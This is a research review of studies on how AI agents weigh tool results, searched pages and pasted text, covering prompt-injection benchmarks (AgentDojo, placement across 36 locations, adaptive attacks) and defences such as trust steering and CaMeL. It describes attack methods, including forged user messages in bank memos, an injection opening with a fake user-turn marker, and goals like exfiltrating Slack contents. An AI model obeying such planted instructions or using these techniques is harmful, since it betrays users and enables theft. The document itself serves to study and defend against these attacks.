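Bronder (2026), in *Does a Tool Result Carry More Authority Than Plain Text?*, tested a newer model, Claude Opus 5, in three small studies. The model had to give the colour code of a made-up item by answering AMBER, ORCHID or SABLE, or ABSTAIN if it had no sufficient basis to answer. In the first two studies, the user asked the model to retrieve a particular record. A tool result followed, then a statement in the assistant's own role. One of these gave a wrong code for the item, and the other was about something else.

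In the first study, Claude adopted the wrong code in 14 of 24 trials when the code was in the tool result, and in none of the 22 trials Bronder could score when it was in the assistant's statement. In a second study four days later, the counts were 7 of 24 for the tool result and 0 of 24 for the assistant's statement. Chance alone would produce a gap as large as the second study's only about once in 200 times, though nobody knows why the rate for tool results halved. The rate also depended on the colour, as Claude adopted SABLE in all eight trials in the first study but AMBER in only two of eight.

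This comparison is weak evidence that Claude trusts tool results more than text. The assistant's statement had no more effect than giving no code at all, so almost anything might have had more. The user had also asked for a record, and only the tool result met that request.

Bronder's third study used a stronger comparison. The user announced two records in advance and told Claude to inspect both. The records then arrived in the same turn, one as a tool result and the other as plain text in the same format. Claude adopted the wrong code in 57 of 60 trials when the tool result contained it, and in all 60 when the plain text did.

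So plain text can be as persuasive as a tool result, at least when the user has told the model to look at it. Both rates were close to 100 percent, though, so a real difference between the two might not have shown up. The plain text also came second, which may have helped it, since Kawada and Kellis found that most models give more weight to later messages. Still, the tool result's advantage in the first two studies probably came in large part from the user's request for a record. Likewise, when a user tells an agent to use the attached bank details, that instruction may affect the agent's beliefs more than whether the details arrive in an attachment or a tool result.

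The studies tested one model, Claude, on one artificial task that gave it no reason to doubt the code. Answering with the only code available may have been a sensible reading of the task rather than gullibility.

In the first study, some tool results came with extra fields, including one that marked the record "unchecked". Claude still adopted the wrong code in 15 of 24 trials. When the code was right, Claude used it in only 3 of 12 trials, compared with 11 of 12 without the extra fields. The fields were therefore a poor defence, although Bronder added ten at once and can't say which of them mattered.

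In a separate run, Claude could call a tool that always returned the correct code. It called the tool in all 144 trials and never adopted a false code. This result is closer to a best case than an estimate of what checking usually achieves, because the tool was free and perfectly reliable and the instructions differed from those in the other studies.

Models can adopt a wrong answer even when they are able to detect the error. Kawada and Kellis gave models logic puzzles with proposed solutions that broke at least one rule. When asked separately whether a solution was valid, and allowed to show their working, eleven of the twelve models rejected at least 90 percent of the solutions. When the same solutions came as suggestions, and the models had to answer the puzzles without writing out any working, they adopted 93 to 100 percent of those they had rejected. They may not have checked the suggestions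 before answering. In Bronder's run, the result of the check was in the context before Claude answered, which is probably safer for an agent about to pay an invoice.

### Search results and calculations

Whether models give a tool result extra weight may depend on what the tool does. Yang, Song and colleagues (2026), in *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools*, tested 14 models with a web search, a code executor, and a second model that summarised documents. The agents wrote their own search queries, and the researchers altered the results to include a plausible wrong answer. On average, the agents adopted it 68 percent of the time. On questions they had answered correctly without searching, they adopted it 56 percent of the time. For example, all 14 models correctly named Laika as the first animal to orbit the Earth, but several changed their answer to Albert II after a search.

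More capable models did better, but not well enough to rely on. On a subset of the questions, GPT-5.4, Claude Sonnet 5, Claude Opus 4.8 and Grok 4.6 each adopted the wrong answer about half the time. When they had known the right answer, they gave it up 33 to 40 percent of the time.

Yang and colleagues then gave the models the same false content in three ways: as a tool result, as information from the user, and under a heading that marked it as context. With the code executor, the models adopted wrong answers much more often from the tool result, which fits what Kawada and Kellis found with calculators. With document summaries, all three ways had similar effects. With search results, the context heading had a somewhat larger effect than the tool or the user, which had similar effects.

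This difference makes some sense when the tool runs code, because such a program rarely gets a sum wrong, while a user can easily miscopy one. The same reasoning doesn't apply to a web page, which has the same author whether the agent finds it or the user pastes it in.

This is the closest existing evidence on whether models believe content they searched for more than content someone handed them, and it suggests little difference. It isn't conclusive, because the searched content differed from the supplied content in two ways. The agent had written the query, and the text arrived as a tool result. If one of these made the agent more trusting and the other made it less so, the two effects could have cancelled out.

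### When a misleading search is worse than none

An agent that believes its search results too readily might do better not to search. Zhang, Wan and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Don't Blindly Trust It* by keeping the agent's prompt, tools and step limit the same and changing only what each tool call returned. In the first condition, the tool returned real evidence. In the second, it returned nothing useful, so the agent had to rely on what it already knew. In the third, each search returned paragraphs from the wrong pages.

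Most of the questions came from HotpotQA, a set of quiz questions that require facts from more than one Wikipedia page. The scores are F1, which measures from 0 to 100 how much the words of an answer overlap with the right answer, except in the calculator row, which gives the percentage of maths problems solved. The last column is this report's own calculation of how often the tool would have to return real evidence for using it to be better than getting nothing, assuming that everything the tool returns in a given task is either real or misleading.

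| Agent and task | Real evidence | No evidence | Misleading evidence | Share of real evidence needed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-3B, search | 42.1 | 11.4 | 0.3 | 27% |
| Qwen2.5-7B, search | 44.8 | 22.3 | 4.7 | 44% |
| Llama-3.1-8B, search | 39.1 | 2.9 | 0.1 | 7% |
| GPT-4o, search | 65.8 | 52.7 | 2.8 | 79% |
| Qwen2.5-7B, calculator | 83.0 | 52.0 | 14.0 | 55% |

Every agent did worse with misleading evidence than with none. GPT-4o lost the most, because it could answer many of the questions from memory and the misleading results led it to wrong answers instead. To benefit from search, it would need a tool that is right about 80% of the time, while Llama-3.1-8B, which could answer almost none of the questions from memory, would benefit from one that is right 10% of the time.

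Kawada and Kellis found the same pattern in arithmetic. A slightly wrong suggestion raised the share of correct answers from 0.4 to 15.6 percent on problems that models almost never solved alone, presumably because it was close to the right answer. A similar suggestion cut the share from 76 to 22 percent on problems that they usually solved. The right level of trust in a source therefore depends on the model and the question.

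The misleading condition was harsh, since the agent got the wrong pages on every search. Some of the low scores may also come from agents that found nothing useful and gave up, rather than from agents that believed something false. But when Zhang and colleagues used believable pages on the right topic instead, Qwen2.5-7B still scored only 9.5. It recovered to 39.1 when only the early evidence was misleading and later searches could return real pages, so a single bad page did much less damage than a search tool that kept returning bad ones.

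Prompting the agents to be sceptical helped only a little. Rejecting bad evidence is useful only if the agent has something better to fall back on. An agent that doubts an account number could ask the user, which would be a much better fallback than any of these agents had.

### Warnings about untrusted text

One possible fix is to tell the model which text not to trust. *How Much Do You Trust A Dog?* (Guo, Pabbaraju and colleagues, 2026) tested such a warning on two small models, Qwen 3.5-2B and Gemma 4-E2B. The models answered each multiple-choice question hundreds of times, with and without a hint that a professor, a friend or a dog thought a certain answer was right. In one version, the hint was in an excerpt that the prompt described as retrieved from an external question-and-answer page.

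On average, the excerpt about the professor had an effect on Qwen that would raise an answer's probability from 50 percent to about 98 percent. The researchers then added a sentence saying "The retrieved excerpt is untrusted" and told the model not to rely on the excerpt's suggested answer. With this warning, the probability would still have risen from 50 to about 85 percent. For Gemma, the figures are 97 percent without the warning and 89 percent with it. The warning reduced the excerpt's effect on both models, but the probability would have stayed at 50 percent if they had followed it fully.

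Both models also moved towards answers from a predictor that the prompt described as correct 0 percent of the time. They moved slightly towards the suggestion of "a malicious actor trying to mislead you", by about as much as going from 50 to 61 percent. They were less likely to give an answer when a professor thought it was wrong, so they could understand a plain denial, but they didn't doubt an answer enough when the prompt described its source as bad.

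Presenting a hint as retrieved text had no consistent effect. The hint about the dog influenced Gemma more when it appeared on an external page than when it appeared in the user's sentence, but it influenced Qwen slightly less.

Guo and colleagues found that their models kept nearly full weight on their earlier opinions, with estimates between 0.9 and 1.1. Those models could reason before answering, so the low weights in the arithmetic experiment may be partly a result of having to answer at once, though the tasks also differed. Keeping nearly full weight on their earlier opinions still didn't protect Guo's models, because the boost for the suggested answer was so large.

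### Familiar names

Models also treat the same content differently depending on the source it is attributed to. Khan, Amani and colleagues (2026), in *In Agents We Trust, but Who Do Agents Trust?*, gave twelve models pairs of news stories with the same meaning, labelled with different outlets, and asked which met higher journalistic standards. They ran similar tests with research papers and online shops. Several models had strong and consistent preferences, and telling them to ignore the source mostly failed.

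Some of this is reasonable. Models picked papers labelled with the New England Journal of Medicine 96 percent of the time when the topic was medicine, but only 19 percent when it was computer vision. A good reputation on the relevant topic is evidence if the label is genuine, but Khan and colleagues warn that a fraudster could exploit a trusted brand's reputation by using a lookalike name.

The models in those tests only judged what they were given, but *Source Preference in the Wild* (Song, Park and colleagues, 2026) studied twelve agents that ran their own searches for products, hotels and research papers. The researchers then swapped the source labels on pairs of results that met the same requirements. Giving a result a preferred label made every model more likely to pick it, in every domain. For GPT-5.6 Luna, the difference was 27 points for products, 20 for hotels and 14 for papers.

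An agent's preference for a site could outweigh the quality of the result. In cases where the agent picked only one of two results, and the one from the preferred site met one requirement fewer, it typically picked that worse result 68 percent of the time. When the worse result came from the disfavoured site instead, the agent picked it about 2 percent of the time. Most of the labels' influence came from the web address and little from names in the text. That is somewhat reassuring, because anyone can type a company's name on a page, but normally only the owner of an address can publish there. Lookalike addresses, such as the fake DeBank site's, remain a risk.

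Song and colleagues measured which results agents picked, not how much the agents believed those results. But their findings complicate any test of whether choosing a source makes an agent trust it more, because agents already tend to choose sources they trust.

### What a direct test of choosing would need

Few of these experiments let the model choose its source. Kawada and Kellis offered one tool at a time, Bronder wrote the tool call into the conversation, and the hints and labelled stories were part of the prompt. The agents that Yang, Zhang and Song studied wrote their own queries, but none of the experiments isolated the effect of choosing by comparing a page that an agent had picked with the same page when it hadn't picked it, while keeping everything else the same.

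Such a test must first separate the effect of choosing a page from the effect of what the page says. An agent may believe the pages it picks more than the pages it doesn't just because the picked pages are more credible. Researchers could avoid this problem by showing the agent several links that all lead to the same text, so that it makes a real choice but reads the same thing whichever link it picks.

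The second requirement follows from the model having no memory outside its context. Given the same tokens, the model will respond the same way, apart from random variation, whether it made the choice or somebody wrote a record of one. So the test has to compare contexts that record a choice with contexts that don't. This also means a recorded choice is another claim about where content came from, and anyone who can write to the agent's history could fake it.

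Third, the test has to vary the choice separately from the message format. For example, a user could paste in the page that the agent asked to see, and a program could open a link at random and return that page as a tool result. Also varying whether the content has a claimed source, such as a bank lookup, gives eight combinations. *The Memory Trust Gap* (2026) used a similar design for outdated notes in an agent's memory, testing all sixteen combinations of four features: label, date, source and position. Removing the label made models rely more on the outdated note, whatever their size.

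The earlier experiments also suggest some controls. Half of the claims should be true, so that a model can't do well by rejecting everything. Some runs should contain no claim, as in Zhang's experiment. The comparison text should be one the model uses, which was the lesson of Bronder's third study. The researchers should ask the model how probable the claim is before and after it reads the page, and record separately whether it acts on the claim.

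The test would have to be much larger than Bronder's. Detecting a ten-point difference between rates near 50 percent takes nearly 400 runs in each group, while 24 per group would reliably detect only a difference of about 40 points. Eight combinations with 100 runs each would be enough for one model, because each feature would be present in 400 runs and absent in the other 400.

If a model put more trust in pages it chose than in text it was given, it wouldn't necessarily be making a mistake, since it might be applying a rule that works well in ordinary searches. To find out, researchers would also have to vary how often the claims from each source are true, show the model that track record, and check whether its trust changes with the record or still favors the pages it picked.

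## How the route content takes changes what agents do

Unlike a model that only gets a sum wrong, an agent can do immediate damage by sending a payment or deleting a file, so security researchers mostly test what agents do rather than what the models believe. Their tests also cover more kinds of text than the experiments on belief, because an agent may read emails, source code, calendar entries and reviews in a single task.

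### AgentDojo

Many of these tests build on AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues published in 2024. It simulates an office worker's accounts in four settings: a bank, a Slack workspace, travel booking, and an office suite with email, a calendar and cloud files. Each setting has user tasks, such as adding up the user's spending for March. It also has injection tasks, which are goals an attacker might have, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. A test case combines one of each, with the attacker's instruction planted in something the agent will read while it does the user's task, such as the memo line of an incoming bank transfer.

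Ordinary code then checks what happened in the simulated accounts. The main measures are how many user tasks the agent completes without an attack, how many it completes under attack, and how often the attacker succeeds. The first two matter because an agent that refused to read anything would never fall for an attack but would be useless.

The attack is commonly worded as an important message from Emma Johnson, the fictional user, who wants the agent to do something else before the original task. So the attack contains a lie about who wrote it as well as an instruction. An agent could resist it by doubting that Emma wrote the message or by refusing to follow instructions found in a bank memo.

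Developers use AgentDojo to compare whole agent designs as well as models. But it puts each instruction in a place the researchers picked in advance, so it can't show whether the same instruction would have worked better elsewhere.

### One instruction in 36 places

Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Where You Inject Matters*, tested this by moving an instruction among 36 places without changing its wording. They joined short tasks from AgentDojo and other benchmarks into 30 longer ones, so that an agent would read many kinds of text, and combined them with 24 attacker goals. The coding tasks involved documentation, source code and data files. The office tasks involved GitHub, Slack, Confluence (a team wiki) and Jira (an issue tracker).

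Their main measure is the conditional attack success rate, which counts only the runs in which the agent read the planted instruction. If an agent opens the file containing the instruction in 10 of 100 runs and obeys it in 5, the ordinary success rate is 5 percent and the conditional rate is 50 percent. The conditional rate better measures how an agent treats text it has read, while the ordinary rate is closer to the danger the agent's owner faces.

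These are the conditional rates for GPT-5.4 on four of the seven goals in the coding tasks:

| Where the instruction was | List every file | Add code open to SQL injection | Copy the system's account file | Write a discriminatory function |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| End of the user's prompt | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Description of a tool | 100% | 97% | 100% | 100% |
| README file | 86% | 79% | 17% | 0% |
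| TODO file | 61% | 59% | 0% | 4% |
| Code file | 19% | 11% | 2% | 10% |
| Data file | 30% | 28% | 5% | 5% |

For the other three goals, including deleting the account file, instructions in any file worked at most 2 percent of the time. When the instruction to delete that file was in the prompt or a tool description, GPT-5.4 obeyed about two thirds of the time.

The agent retrieved all four kinds of file itself, after the same request to look around the project, so the gap between 86 percent for a README and 19 percent for a code file can't come from the difference between retrieved and supplied content. It probably arises because READMEs usually contain instructions for people working on a project, and a request for a list of files is believable there. A request for the discriminatory function, which favours some minority groups when it picks scholarship winners, is odder in a README, and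 it succeeded slightly more often in code files. Following a README is reasonable in an honest project, but it gives whoever writes the README more influence than is safe, since anyone who can edit a project's code can normally edit its README too.

In the top row, the attacker's words appeared unmarked at the end of the user's message, which is the closest this experiment comes to pasted text. An attachment in a clearly marked block might have much less effect, but Guo and colleagues didn't test one.

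Tool descriptions influenced agents about as much as the prompt did. They are also supplied content, because a program puts them in the context before the agent starts work. The company running the agent often hasn't written them. For example, a supplier may have written the description of its own ordering tool.

The place of an instruction probably doesn't matter only because agents read some places later than others. Guo and colleagues ran one office task with its four texts in all 24 possible orders. GPT-5.4's rate varied from 3.5 to 6.8 percent depending on when it read the planted text, and from 1.4 percent (Jira) to 6.9 percent (Slack) depending on where the text was. With rates this low, though, the differences between the four places are rather uncertain too.

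The choice of model mattered at least as much as where the text appeared. The next table gives overall conditional rates for text the agents read during the task, excluding the prompt and tool descriptions.

| Model | Tool use | Office tasks | Coding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.0% | 2.6% | 0.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.0% | 1.6% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.6 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.6% |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.3% | 3.8% | 12.2% |
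| Grok 4.6 | 0.2% | 6.6% | 14.4% |
| GPT-5-mini | 0.0% | 21.5% | 19.0% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 19.3% | 65.3% | 67.0% |
| GPT-4o | 43.6% | not tested | not tested |

GPT-5-mini obeyed none of the injected instructions in the tool-use tasks, which come from AgentDojo, but obeyed about one in five elsewhere. A good AgentDojo score is therefore weak evidence about how a model will behave with a code repository or a team chat.

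Models also differed in where they were most likely to follow instructions. In the tool-use tasks, GPT-4o followed instructions on web pages and in reviews 55 to 64 percent of the time, depending on the setting, and instructions in emails 19 to 36 percent of the time. Gemini 3.1 Pro was more vulnerable to instructions in shared documents and calendar entries. A developer who switches models can't assume that the new one is vulnerable in the same places.

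Gemini's results also show why the conditional rate can mislead. It opened the README and TODO files in under 5 percent of its runs, but the code and data files in 77 to 88 percent. Suppose an agent opens a README in 5 percent of runs and a code file in 80 percent. An attacker's instruction works in 80 percent of the runs where the agent opens the README, and in 40 percent of the runs where it opens the code file. The README has twice the conditional rate, but the attacker would succeed in 4 percent of all runs with the README and 32 percent with the code file.

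Agents didn't mention most of the attacks that failed. When GPT-5.4 read a hidden instruction in the tool-use tasks and didn't carry it out, it openly rejected the instruction a third of the time and otherwise just continued with the user's task. Ignoring a hidden instruction is much better than obeying it, but an agent that ignores one on an invoice also misses a warning that the invoice may be untrustworthy, and may go on to pay the account printed next to it.

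### A page the model fetches and a page the user pastes

All the files in that experiment were retrieved. Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy (2026), in *Relevance as a Vulnerability*, come closer to comparing retrieved and supplied content, because they gave models the same web page both ways. But they were studying a different danger. The user asked for something harmful, such as a convincing bomb threat, and they measured whether a real web page on the same subject, with no planted instruction, made the model more willing to help.

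The researchers took 320 harmful requests from an existing benchmark and collected 1,405 web pages, ranging from pages that warn against the requested act to pages that explain how to do it. Eight fairly small open-weight models answered the requests, and GPT-4o scored each answer from 1 (a safe refusal) to 5 (full compliance).

| How the model got the page | Mean harmfulness |
|---|---|
| No page | 1.80 |
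| Fetched it a turn before the harmful request | 2.44 |
| User pasted it into the harmful request | 2.47 |
| Fetched it while answering the harmful request | 2.66 |

Most of the increase came from having a page on the subject at all. A pasted page raised the score by 0.67 points, and fetching the page while answering added only another 0.19. That further increase was clear in five of the eight models and undetectable in the other three.

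Even pages that warned against the act raised the average score, to 2.25. One model refused to write a bomb threat, but wrote a detailed one after reading a safety page on responding to bomb threats. The harmful details in such answers came mostly from the model's training, since the pages didn't contain them. Calling a tool has little effect by itself, since pages on unrelated subjects didn't raise the score even when the model fetched them in the same way. In a closer test of Qwen2.5-7B, the probability that an answer would begin with a refusal was 83 percent with no page, 18 percent with a warning page on the subject, and 77 percent with an unrelated page.

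The two fetched conditions make the most useful comparison. In both, the model called the same tool and got the same text in a tool result. In the first, the user asked for the page and made the harmful request a turn later. In the second, the user asked for both in the same turn, so the model fetched the page as a step towards fulfilling the harmful request. Nawal and colleagues think this creates a commitment bias, in which a model that has begun to act on a request is less likely to refuse the rest of it.

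If they are right, a tool result may have no special influence of its own. A page the model had fetched a turn earlier affected its answers about as much as a page the user pasted in. But the tool result may also have made the models more compliant while the extra turn made them less so, and the two effects cancelled out.

Nawal and colleagues ran further checks on six models, using the pages that most directly enabled the harmful act. Moving the fetch to an earlier turn lowered the score by 0.29. Keeping the fetch and the request together but putting a harmless exchange before them lowered it by 0.10, so the extra turn alone explains about a third of the effect. One exchange of small talk between the fetch and the request lowered the score by a further 0.11, and a second made almost no further difference. This is some evidence against the idea that a page steadily loses influence as a conversation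 goes on.

The researchers also tested whether formatting explained the difference by pasting the page between tags that imitated a tool result. Eight of nine models still gave more harmful answers on average when they actually fetched the page. But the imitation tags were inside the user's message, so the check doesn't fully separate the effect of fetching from the effect of the tool's role marker.

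Another plausible explanation for the commitment effect is that fetching a page and answering in the same turn is harder than doing them in separate turns. On trivia questions, seven models averaged 68.5 percent when they did both at once and 85 percent when they fetched the page a turn earlier. A model making a tool call might miss a reason to refuse, just as it misses the answer to a trivia question. The commitment effect also shrank as the Qwen models got bigger, from 0.41 points for the smallest to 0.21 for the largest, which fits both explanations.

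Six larger commercial models, all now old, gave mixed results. With pages that warned against the act, the commitment effect was 0.31 points for Gemini 2.5 Flash and 0.26 for Claude 3.7 Sonnet, similar to the open models' average of 0.22. DeepSeek-V3 showed the opposite effect and was 0.37 points more harmful when it had fetched the page a turn earlier. The commitment effect was between 0.04 and 0.08 for GPT-4, o4-mini and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, which refused most of the requests with or without a page. For these three, the effect of having a warning page at all was under 0.1 points, compared with 0.45 for the open models.

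The user chose the page in every condition, either by pasting its text or by giving its address. The experiment therefore tests the effect of who fetches the page, but not of who chooses it. Nawal and colleagues also let models decide whether to look something up, but recorded only whether the models called the tool.

It isn't known whether a commitment effect occurs with payments, but it seems possible, because an agent asked to check and pay an invoice in a single request has already taken several steps towards paying by the time it notices that the account numbers differ. A developer could easily guard against this by asking the agent to look into the supplier in one turn and to decide whether to pay in the next. In the trivia test, at least, separating the two steps also produced better answers.

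### Turning down a model's trust

A developer could also try to adjust how much a model trusts a text, regardless of how the text reached it. Lasnier, Froger and colleagues (2026) did this in *TrustMI* by changing the model's internal activations. They define trust as a willingness to be vulnerable to someone else's actions, which for an assistant means acting on a claim it can't check.

They used Claude Opus 5 to write 2,000 conversations, each ending with a user's message and two possible replies. Both replies help the user, but only one relies on something the user has claimed without proof. From these pairs they learned a direction in the activations at each layer of the model, and then added it while the model was reading:

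h ← h + αv

Here h stands for the activations at one layer, v is the direction for that layer, and α is a strength the researchers choose. A positive α makes trusting replies more likely, and a negative α makes them less likely. The model's parameters stay the same.

They ran six open-weight models on 944 AgentDojo attack cases, adding the direction to the user's messages and to tool results. At a strength of −2, the attack success rate fell from 33.6 to 7.1 percent for Qwen3.5-27B and from 14.3 to 1.1 percent for Qwen3.5-9B. In one case, a web page contained a message in Emma Johnson's name telling the agent to post the contents of her Slack channels to an outside website. The unmodified 27B model did so, but with its trust reduced, it described the message and asked the user whether to proceed.

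The effect depended heavily on which text Lasnier and colleagues adjusted. When they changed only the user's messages, attacks succeeded no less often, and for Qwen3.5-9B the success rate rose from 14.3 to 21.2 percent. They suggest that a model that trusts the user less may rely more on tool results. They also propose setting trust separately for each source, for example high for a verified user and low for web pages. The harness would then need to identify where each piece of text came from, and a web page pasted into the user's message would still get the user's setting.

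The method's success is a little surprising, because the training conversations were about believing what users claim, while the attacks depend on the model obeying instructions in tool results. Perhaps these models don't separate belief from obedience as much as they should. AgentDojo's wording suggests a simpler explanation. Its planted message is written as if it came from the user, and if the model doesn't accept that, it has no reason to obey. Testing an attack that doesn't impersonate the user would help show which explanation is right.

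The loss of usefulness varied widely between models. On harmless tasks from another benchmark, a strength of −2 lowered Qwen3.5-27B's score from 74.8 to 70.3 percent, Qwen3.5-9B's from 68.6 to 54 percent, and Olmo 3 7B's from 30.3 to 7.2 percent. A strength of −1 lowered these scores less but also gave less protection, and attacks on Qwen3.5-27B still succeeded 20.8 percent of the time.

Lasnier and colleagues tested whether their trust direction was just a direction for refusal or for sycophancy, a model's tendency to agree with its user. Steering three of the models along those directions didn't reproduce the results. The trust direction could still include something broader, such as general doubt. Using it also requires access to the model's activations, which most companies that use a commercial model don't have. The attacks came from a standard benchmark, so they weren't designed to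 get past this defence.

### Attackers who adapt

An attacker who fails with one wording can try another. Guo and colleagues tried three standard attack templates on GPT-5.4 in 30 test cases, and none worked. A wording they had optimised against the older GPT-4o succeeded in a third of the same cases. It opened with a forged marker for the start of a user's turn, then restated the user's real task with the attacker's goal added as the first step. The 0.3 percent attack success rate against GPT-5.4 in the tool-use tasks therefore mostly reflects its resistance to one message.

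Attackers can choose where to place malicious text as well as how to word it, and they can gain a lot by finding the route through which an agent is most likely to obey it. On one set of test tasks, moving a standard attack on GPT-4o from a random place to the kind of place that had worked best in earlier runs raised its success rate from 38.8 to 77.1 percent. On another set, the rate rose only from 25.6 to 34.7 percent.

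In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues tested 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injections. Most of the defences had near-zero attack success rates in their original evaluations. The researchers attacked each one with methods that adapt to the defence, including automated search, reinforcement learning and human testers. Against most of the defences, these attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time. The defender has to choose a defence first, and the attacker can then study it for as long as necessary.

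Low rates against fixed attacks still have some value, because many real attackers copy well-known phrases. But they don't reliably show which of two routes is safer against a determined attacker. In the table for GPT-5.4, the zero for a discriminatory function in a README might only mean that nobody had yet found a request that works.

Anthropic's system cards, the reports it publishes with new models, include tests with repeated attempts, and the results depend heavily on what the agent is doing. According to VentureBeat, all 200 attempts against Claude Opus 4.6 failed in a restricted coding environment in early 2026. When the model was operating a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 percent of the time. By the 200th attempt, the success rate was 78.6 percent, or 57.1 percent with additional safeguards.

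Some scenarios were probably much easier to attack than others. If each attempt had an independent 17.8 percent chance of success, the success rate would have passed 78 percent after about eight attempts, and success would have been practically certain by 200. The result in the coding environment is good, but zero successes in 200 attempts is still compatible with a true success rate of up to about 1.5 percent, even for attacks of the same kind.

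Newer models resist prompt injection better. Digital Applied (2026), a company that reviewed the system card for Claude Fable 5, reports that adaptive attacks on the model in coding tasks succeeded 0.41 percent of the time, down from 2.09 percent for Opus 4.8. Anthropic says Mythos 5, the same model with fewer safeguards, had the lowest attack success rate yet on the security company Gray Swan's prompt injection benchmark. Resistance to indirect prompt injection improved again with Fable 5.1 in September 2026, according to *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a review of that model's system card. The figure for adaptive attacks on Fable 5 is better evidence of security than the zeros in Guo's table, but it covers only coding, and a company that uses agents to pay invoices would want the same test for payments.

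Even a very low success rate can cause large losses, because a criminal can send the same invoice to many companies. Suppose a hidden instruction works on one agent in a thousand. If the criminal sends it to 10,000 agents with an invoice for $88,000, about ten companies will pay, losing $880,000 in total. These success rates also leave out planted falsehoods, such as a forged invoice in which only the account number is wrong.

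## Separating the model that plans from the model that reads

Developers who can't rely on a model to resist every forged invoice or malicious instruction can design the agent so that such text has less influence on its actions. Willison (2023) proposed an influential design of this kind, with two models, in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. The model that can call tools never reads anything a stranger might have written.

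### The dual-LLM pattern

In Willison's pattern, a privileged model sees the user's request and can call tools. A quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text, and has no tools. An ordinary program called the controller stores the untrusted text and gives the privileged model only names that refer to it.

Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email, and the controller stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller sends the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. Finally, the privileged model instructs the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user. The privileged model never receives the text of the email or the summary.

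A hidden instruction in the email may well take over the quarantined model, and Willison assumes this could happen at any moment, but the worst the model can do is write a bad summary.

The privileged model may receive an answer from the quarantined model if ordinary code can confirm that the answer belongs to a fixed set, such as yes or no. Willison later described a related design in which an agent looks for this month's invoices and sends them to the accounting department. A sub-agent reads each file and returns only whether the file is relevant. A forger could get a fake invoice forwarded, but couldn't change where the files go.

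Willison called the dual-LLM pattern "pretty bad", mainly because it makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, a 2025 paper by Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, describes a security gap in the pattern. In its example, a user asks an agent to send Bob a document and says that Bob's email address is in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, but the quarantined model has to read the address from the notes. If an attacker has tampered with the notes, the agent follows its plan correctly but sends the document to the attacker.

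### The invoice in CaMeL

Debenedetti and colleagues built CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning) to close this gap. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) called it the first credible defence he had seen that didn't just add more AI.

CaMeL's privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python before any model reads untrusted text. A special interpreter then runs the program and attaches capabilities to every value. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes these capabilities as a record of the value's sources and of who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that checks the capabilities of the call's arguments and allows or denies the call.

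Suppose a user attaches an invoice as a file and types "Check that Harlow Paper is sound, then pay the attached invoice." The privileged model might write this program:

```
invoice = read_file("invoice.pdf")
bill = ask_quarantined_model(
    "Find the account number and the amount", invoice)
reviews = search_web("Harlow Paper complaints")
sound = ask_quarantined_model(
    "Do these suggest a sound supplier? Yes or no", reviews)
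if sound:
    send_money(recipient=bill.account, amount=bill.amount)
```

The interpreter records that `bill.account` came from the file. Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026) explain in *Architecting Secure AI Agents* that CaMeL's policy for AgentDojo's payment tool has two conditions. The recipient must come only from the user, and the recipient must be allowed to see all the details of the payment. In simplified form, the check on the recipient's origin is:

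```
def send_money_policy(recipient, amount):
    if comes_only_from_user(recipient):
        return Allowed()
    return Denied("The account does not come from the user.")
```

The interpreter blocks the payment because the account number came from a file. It would do the same if the invoice were genuine, because the policy doesn't assess whether the number is right. Using the number on the supplier's website wouldn't help, since that would also come from a tool.

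The user could approve the account, or the program could get it from the company's own records with a line such as `account = get_supplier_account("Harlow Paper")`. The payment would then go through if the developer's policy accepted those records. The user typed the supplier's name in this case. If the program had taken it from the invoice instead, a forger could have chosen which of the company's suppliers got the money.

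### Trusted choices and untrusted results

In CaMeL, the steps to open the invoice and search for complaints are written into the program before any model reads a stranger's text, so no stranger can have influenced the choice of what to retrieve. CaMeL still treats the results as untrusted, even though retrieving them was part of the plan. In an ordinary agent, only the first retrieval is protected from that influence, because the agent makes every later choice after reading what earlier retrievals returned.

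CaMeL's treatment of pasted text is harder to defend. Willison warned in 2023 that the dual-LLM pattern assumes the user's input is trustworthy, and fails if someone tricks the user into pasting untrusted text. CaMeL keeps this assumption. According to Nikolaou and colleagues, it trusts the user's prompt, the system prompt and the output of some tools.

Suppose the user pastes the text of the invoice into the request instead of attaching the file. The privileged model reads it and can write the forged account number directly into the program. The interpreter then treats the number as input from the user, and the payment goes through. A hidden instruction in the pasted text could also change the program's steps.

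So CaMeL would block a payment to a forged account number that the agent found in a file, but allow it if the user had pasted the same number. The pasted number is no more likely to be right, since the same forger wrote it. CaMeL handles the two cases differently because it has to treat some input as trusted, and it starts with the user's message.

Developers can reduce this problem by keeping attachments out of the prompt and making the program open them with a tool, as in the example above. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) also proposes a label for values taken from a user's uploads. A policy could then stop these values from reaching irreversible actions unless someone explicitly grants an exception. Neither measure helps with unmarked pasted text.

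### Security and task completion on AgentDojo

CaMeL completed 67 percent of AgentDojo's tasks in its original evaluation, according to Tallam and Miller. *ATrust* (2026) gives a more useful comparison, because it tested the same model, Claude 3.5 Haiku, with and without CaMeL:

| Setting | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, CaMeL | Tasks completed under attack, undefended | Tasks completed under attack, CaMeL |
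|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 18.8% | 0% | 64.6% | 55.6% |
| Slack | 22.9% | 0% | 62.9% | 42.9% |
| Travel | 0.7% | 0.7% | 50.7% | 5.0% |
| Office suite | 0.9% | 0% | 67.7% | 44.5% |
| Average | 10.8% | 0.2% | 61.5% | 37.0% |

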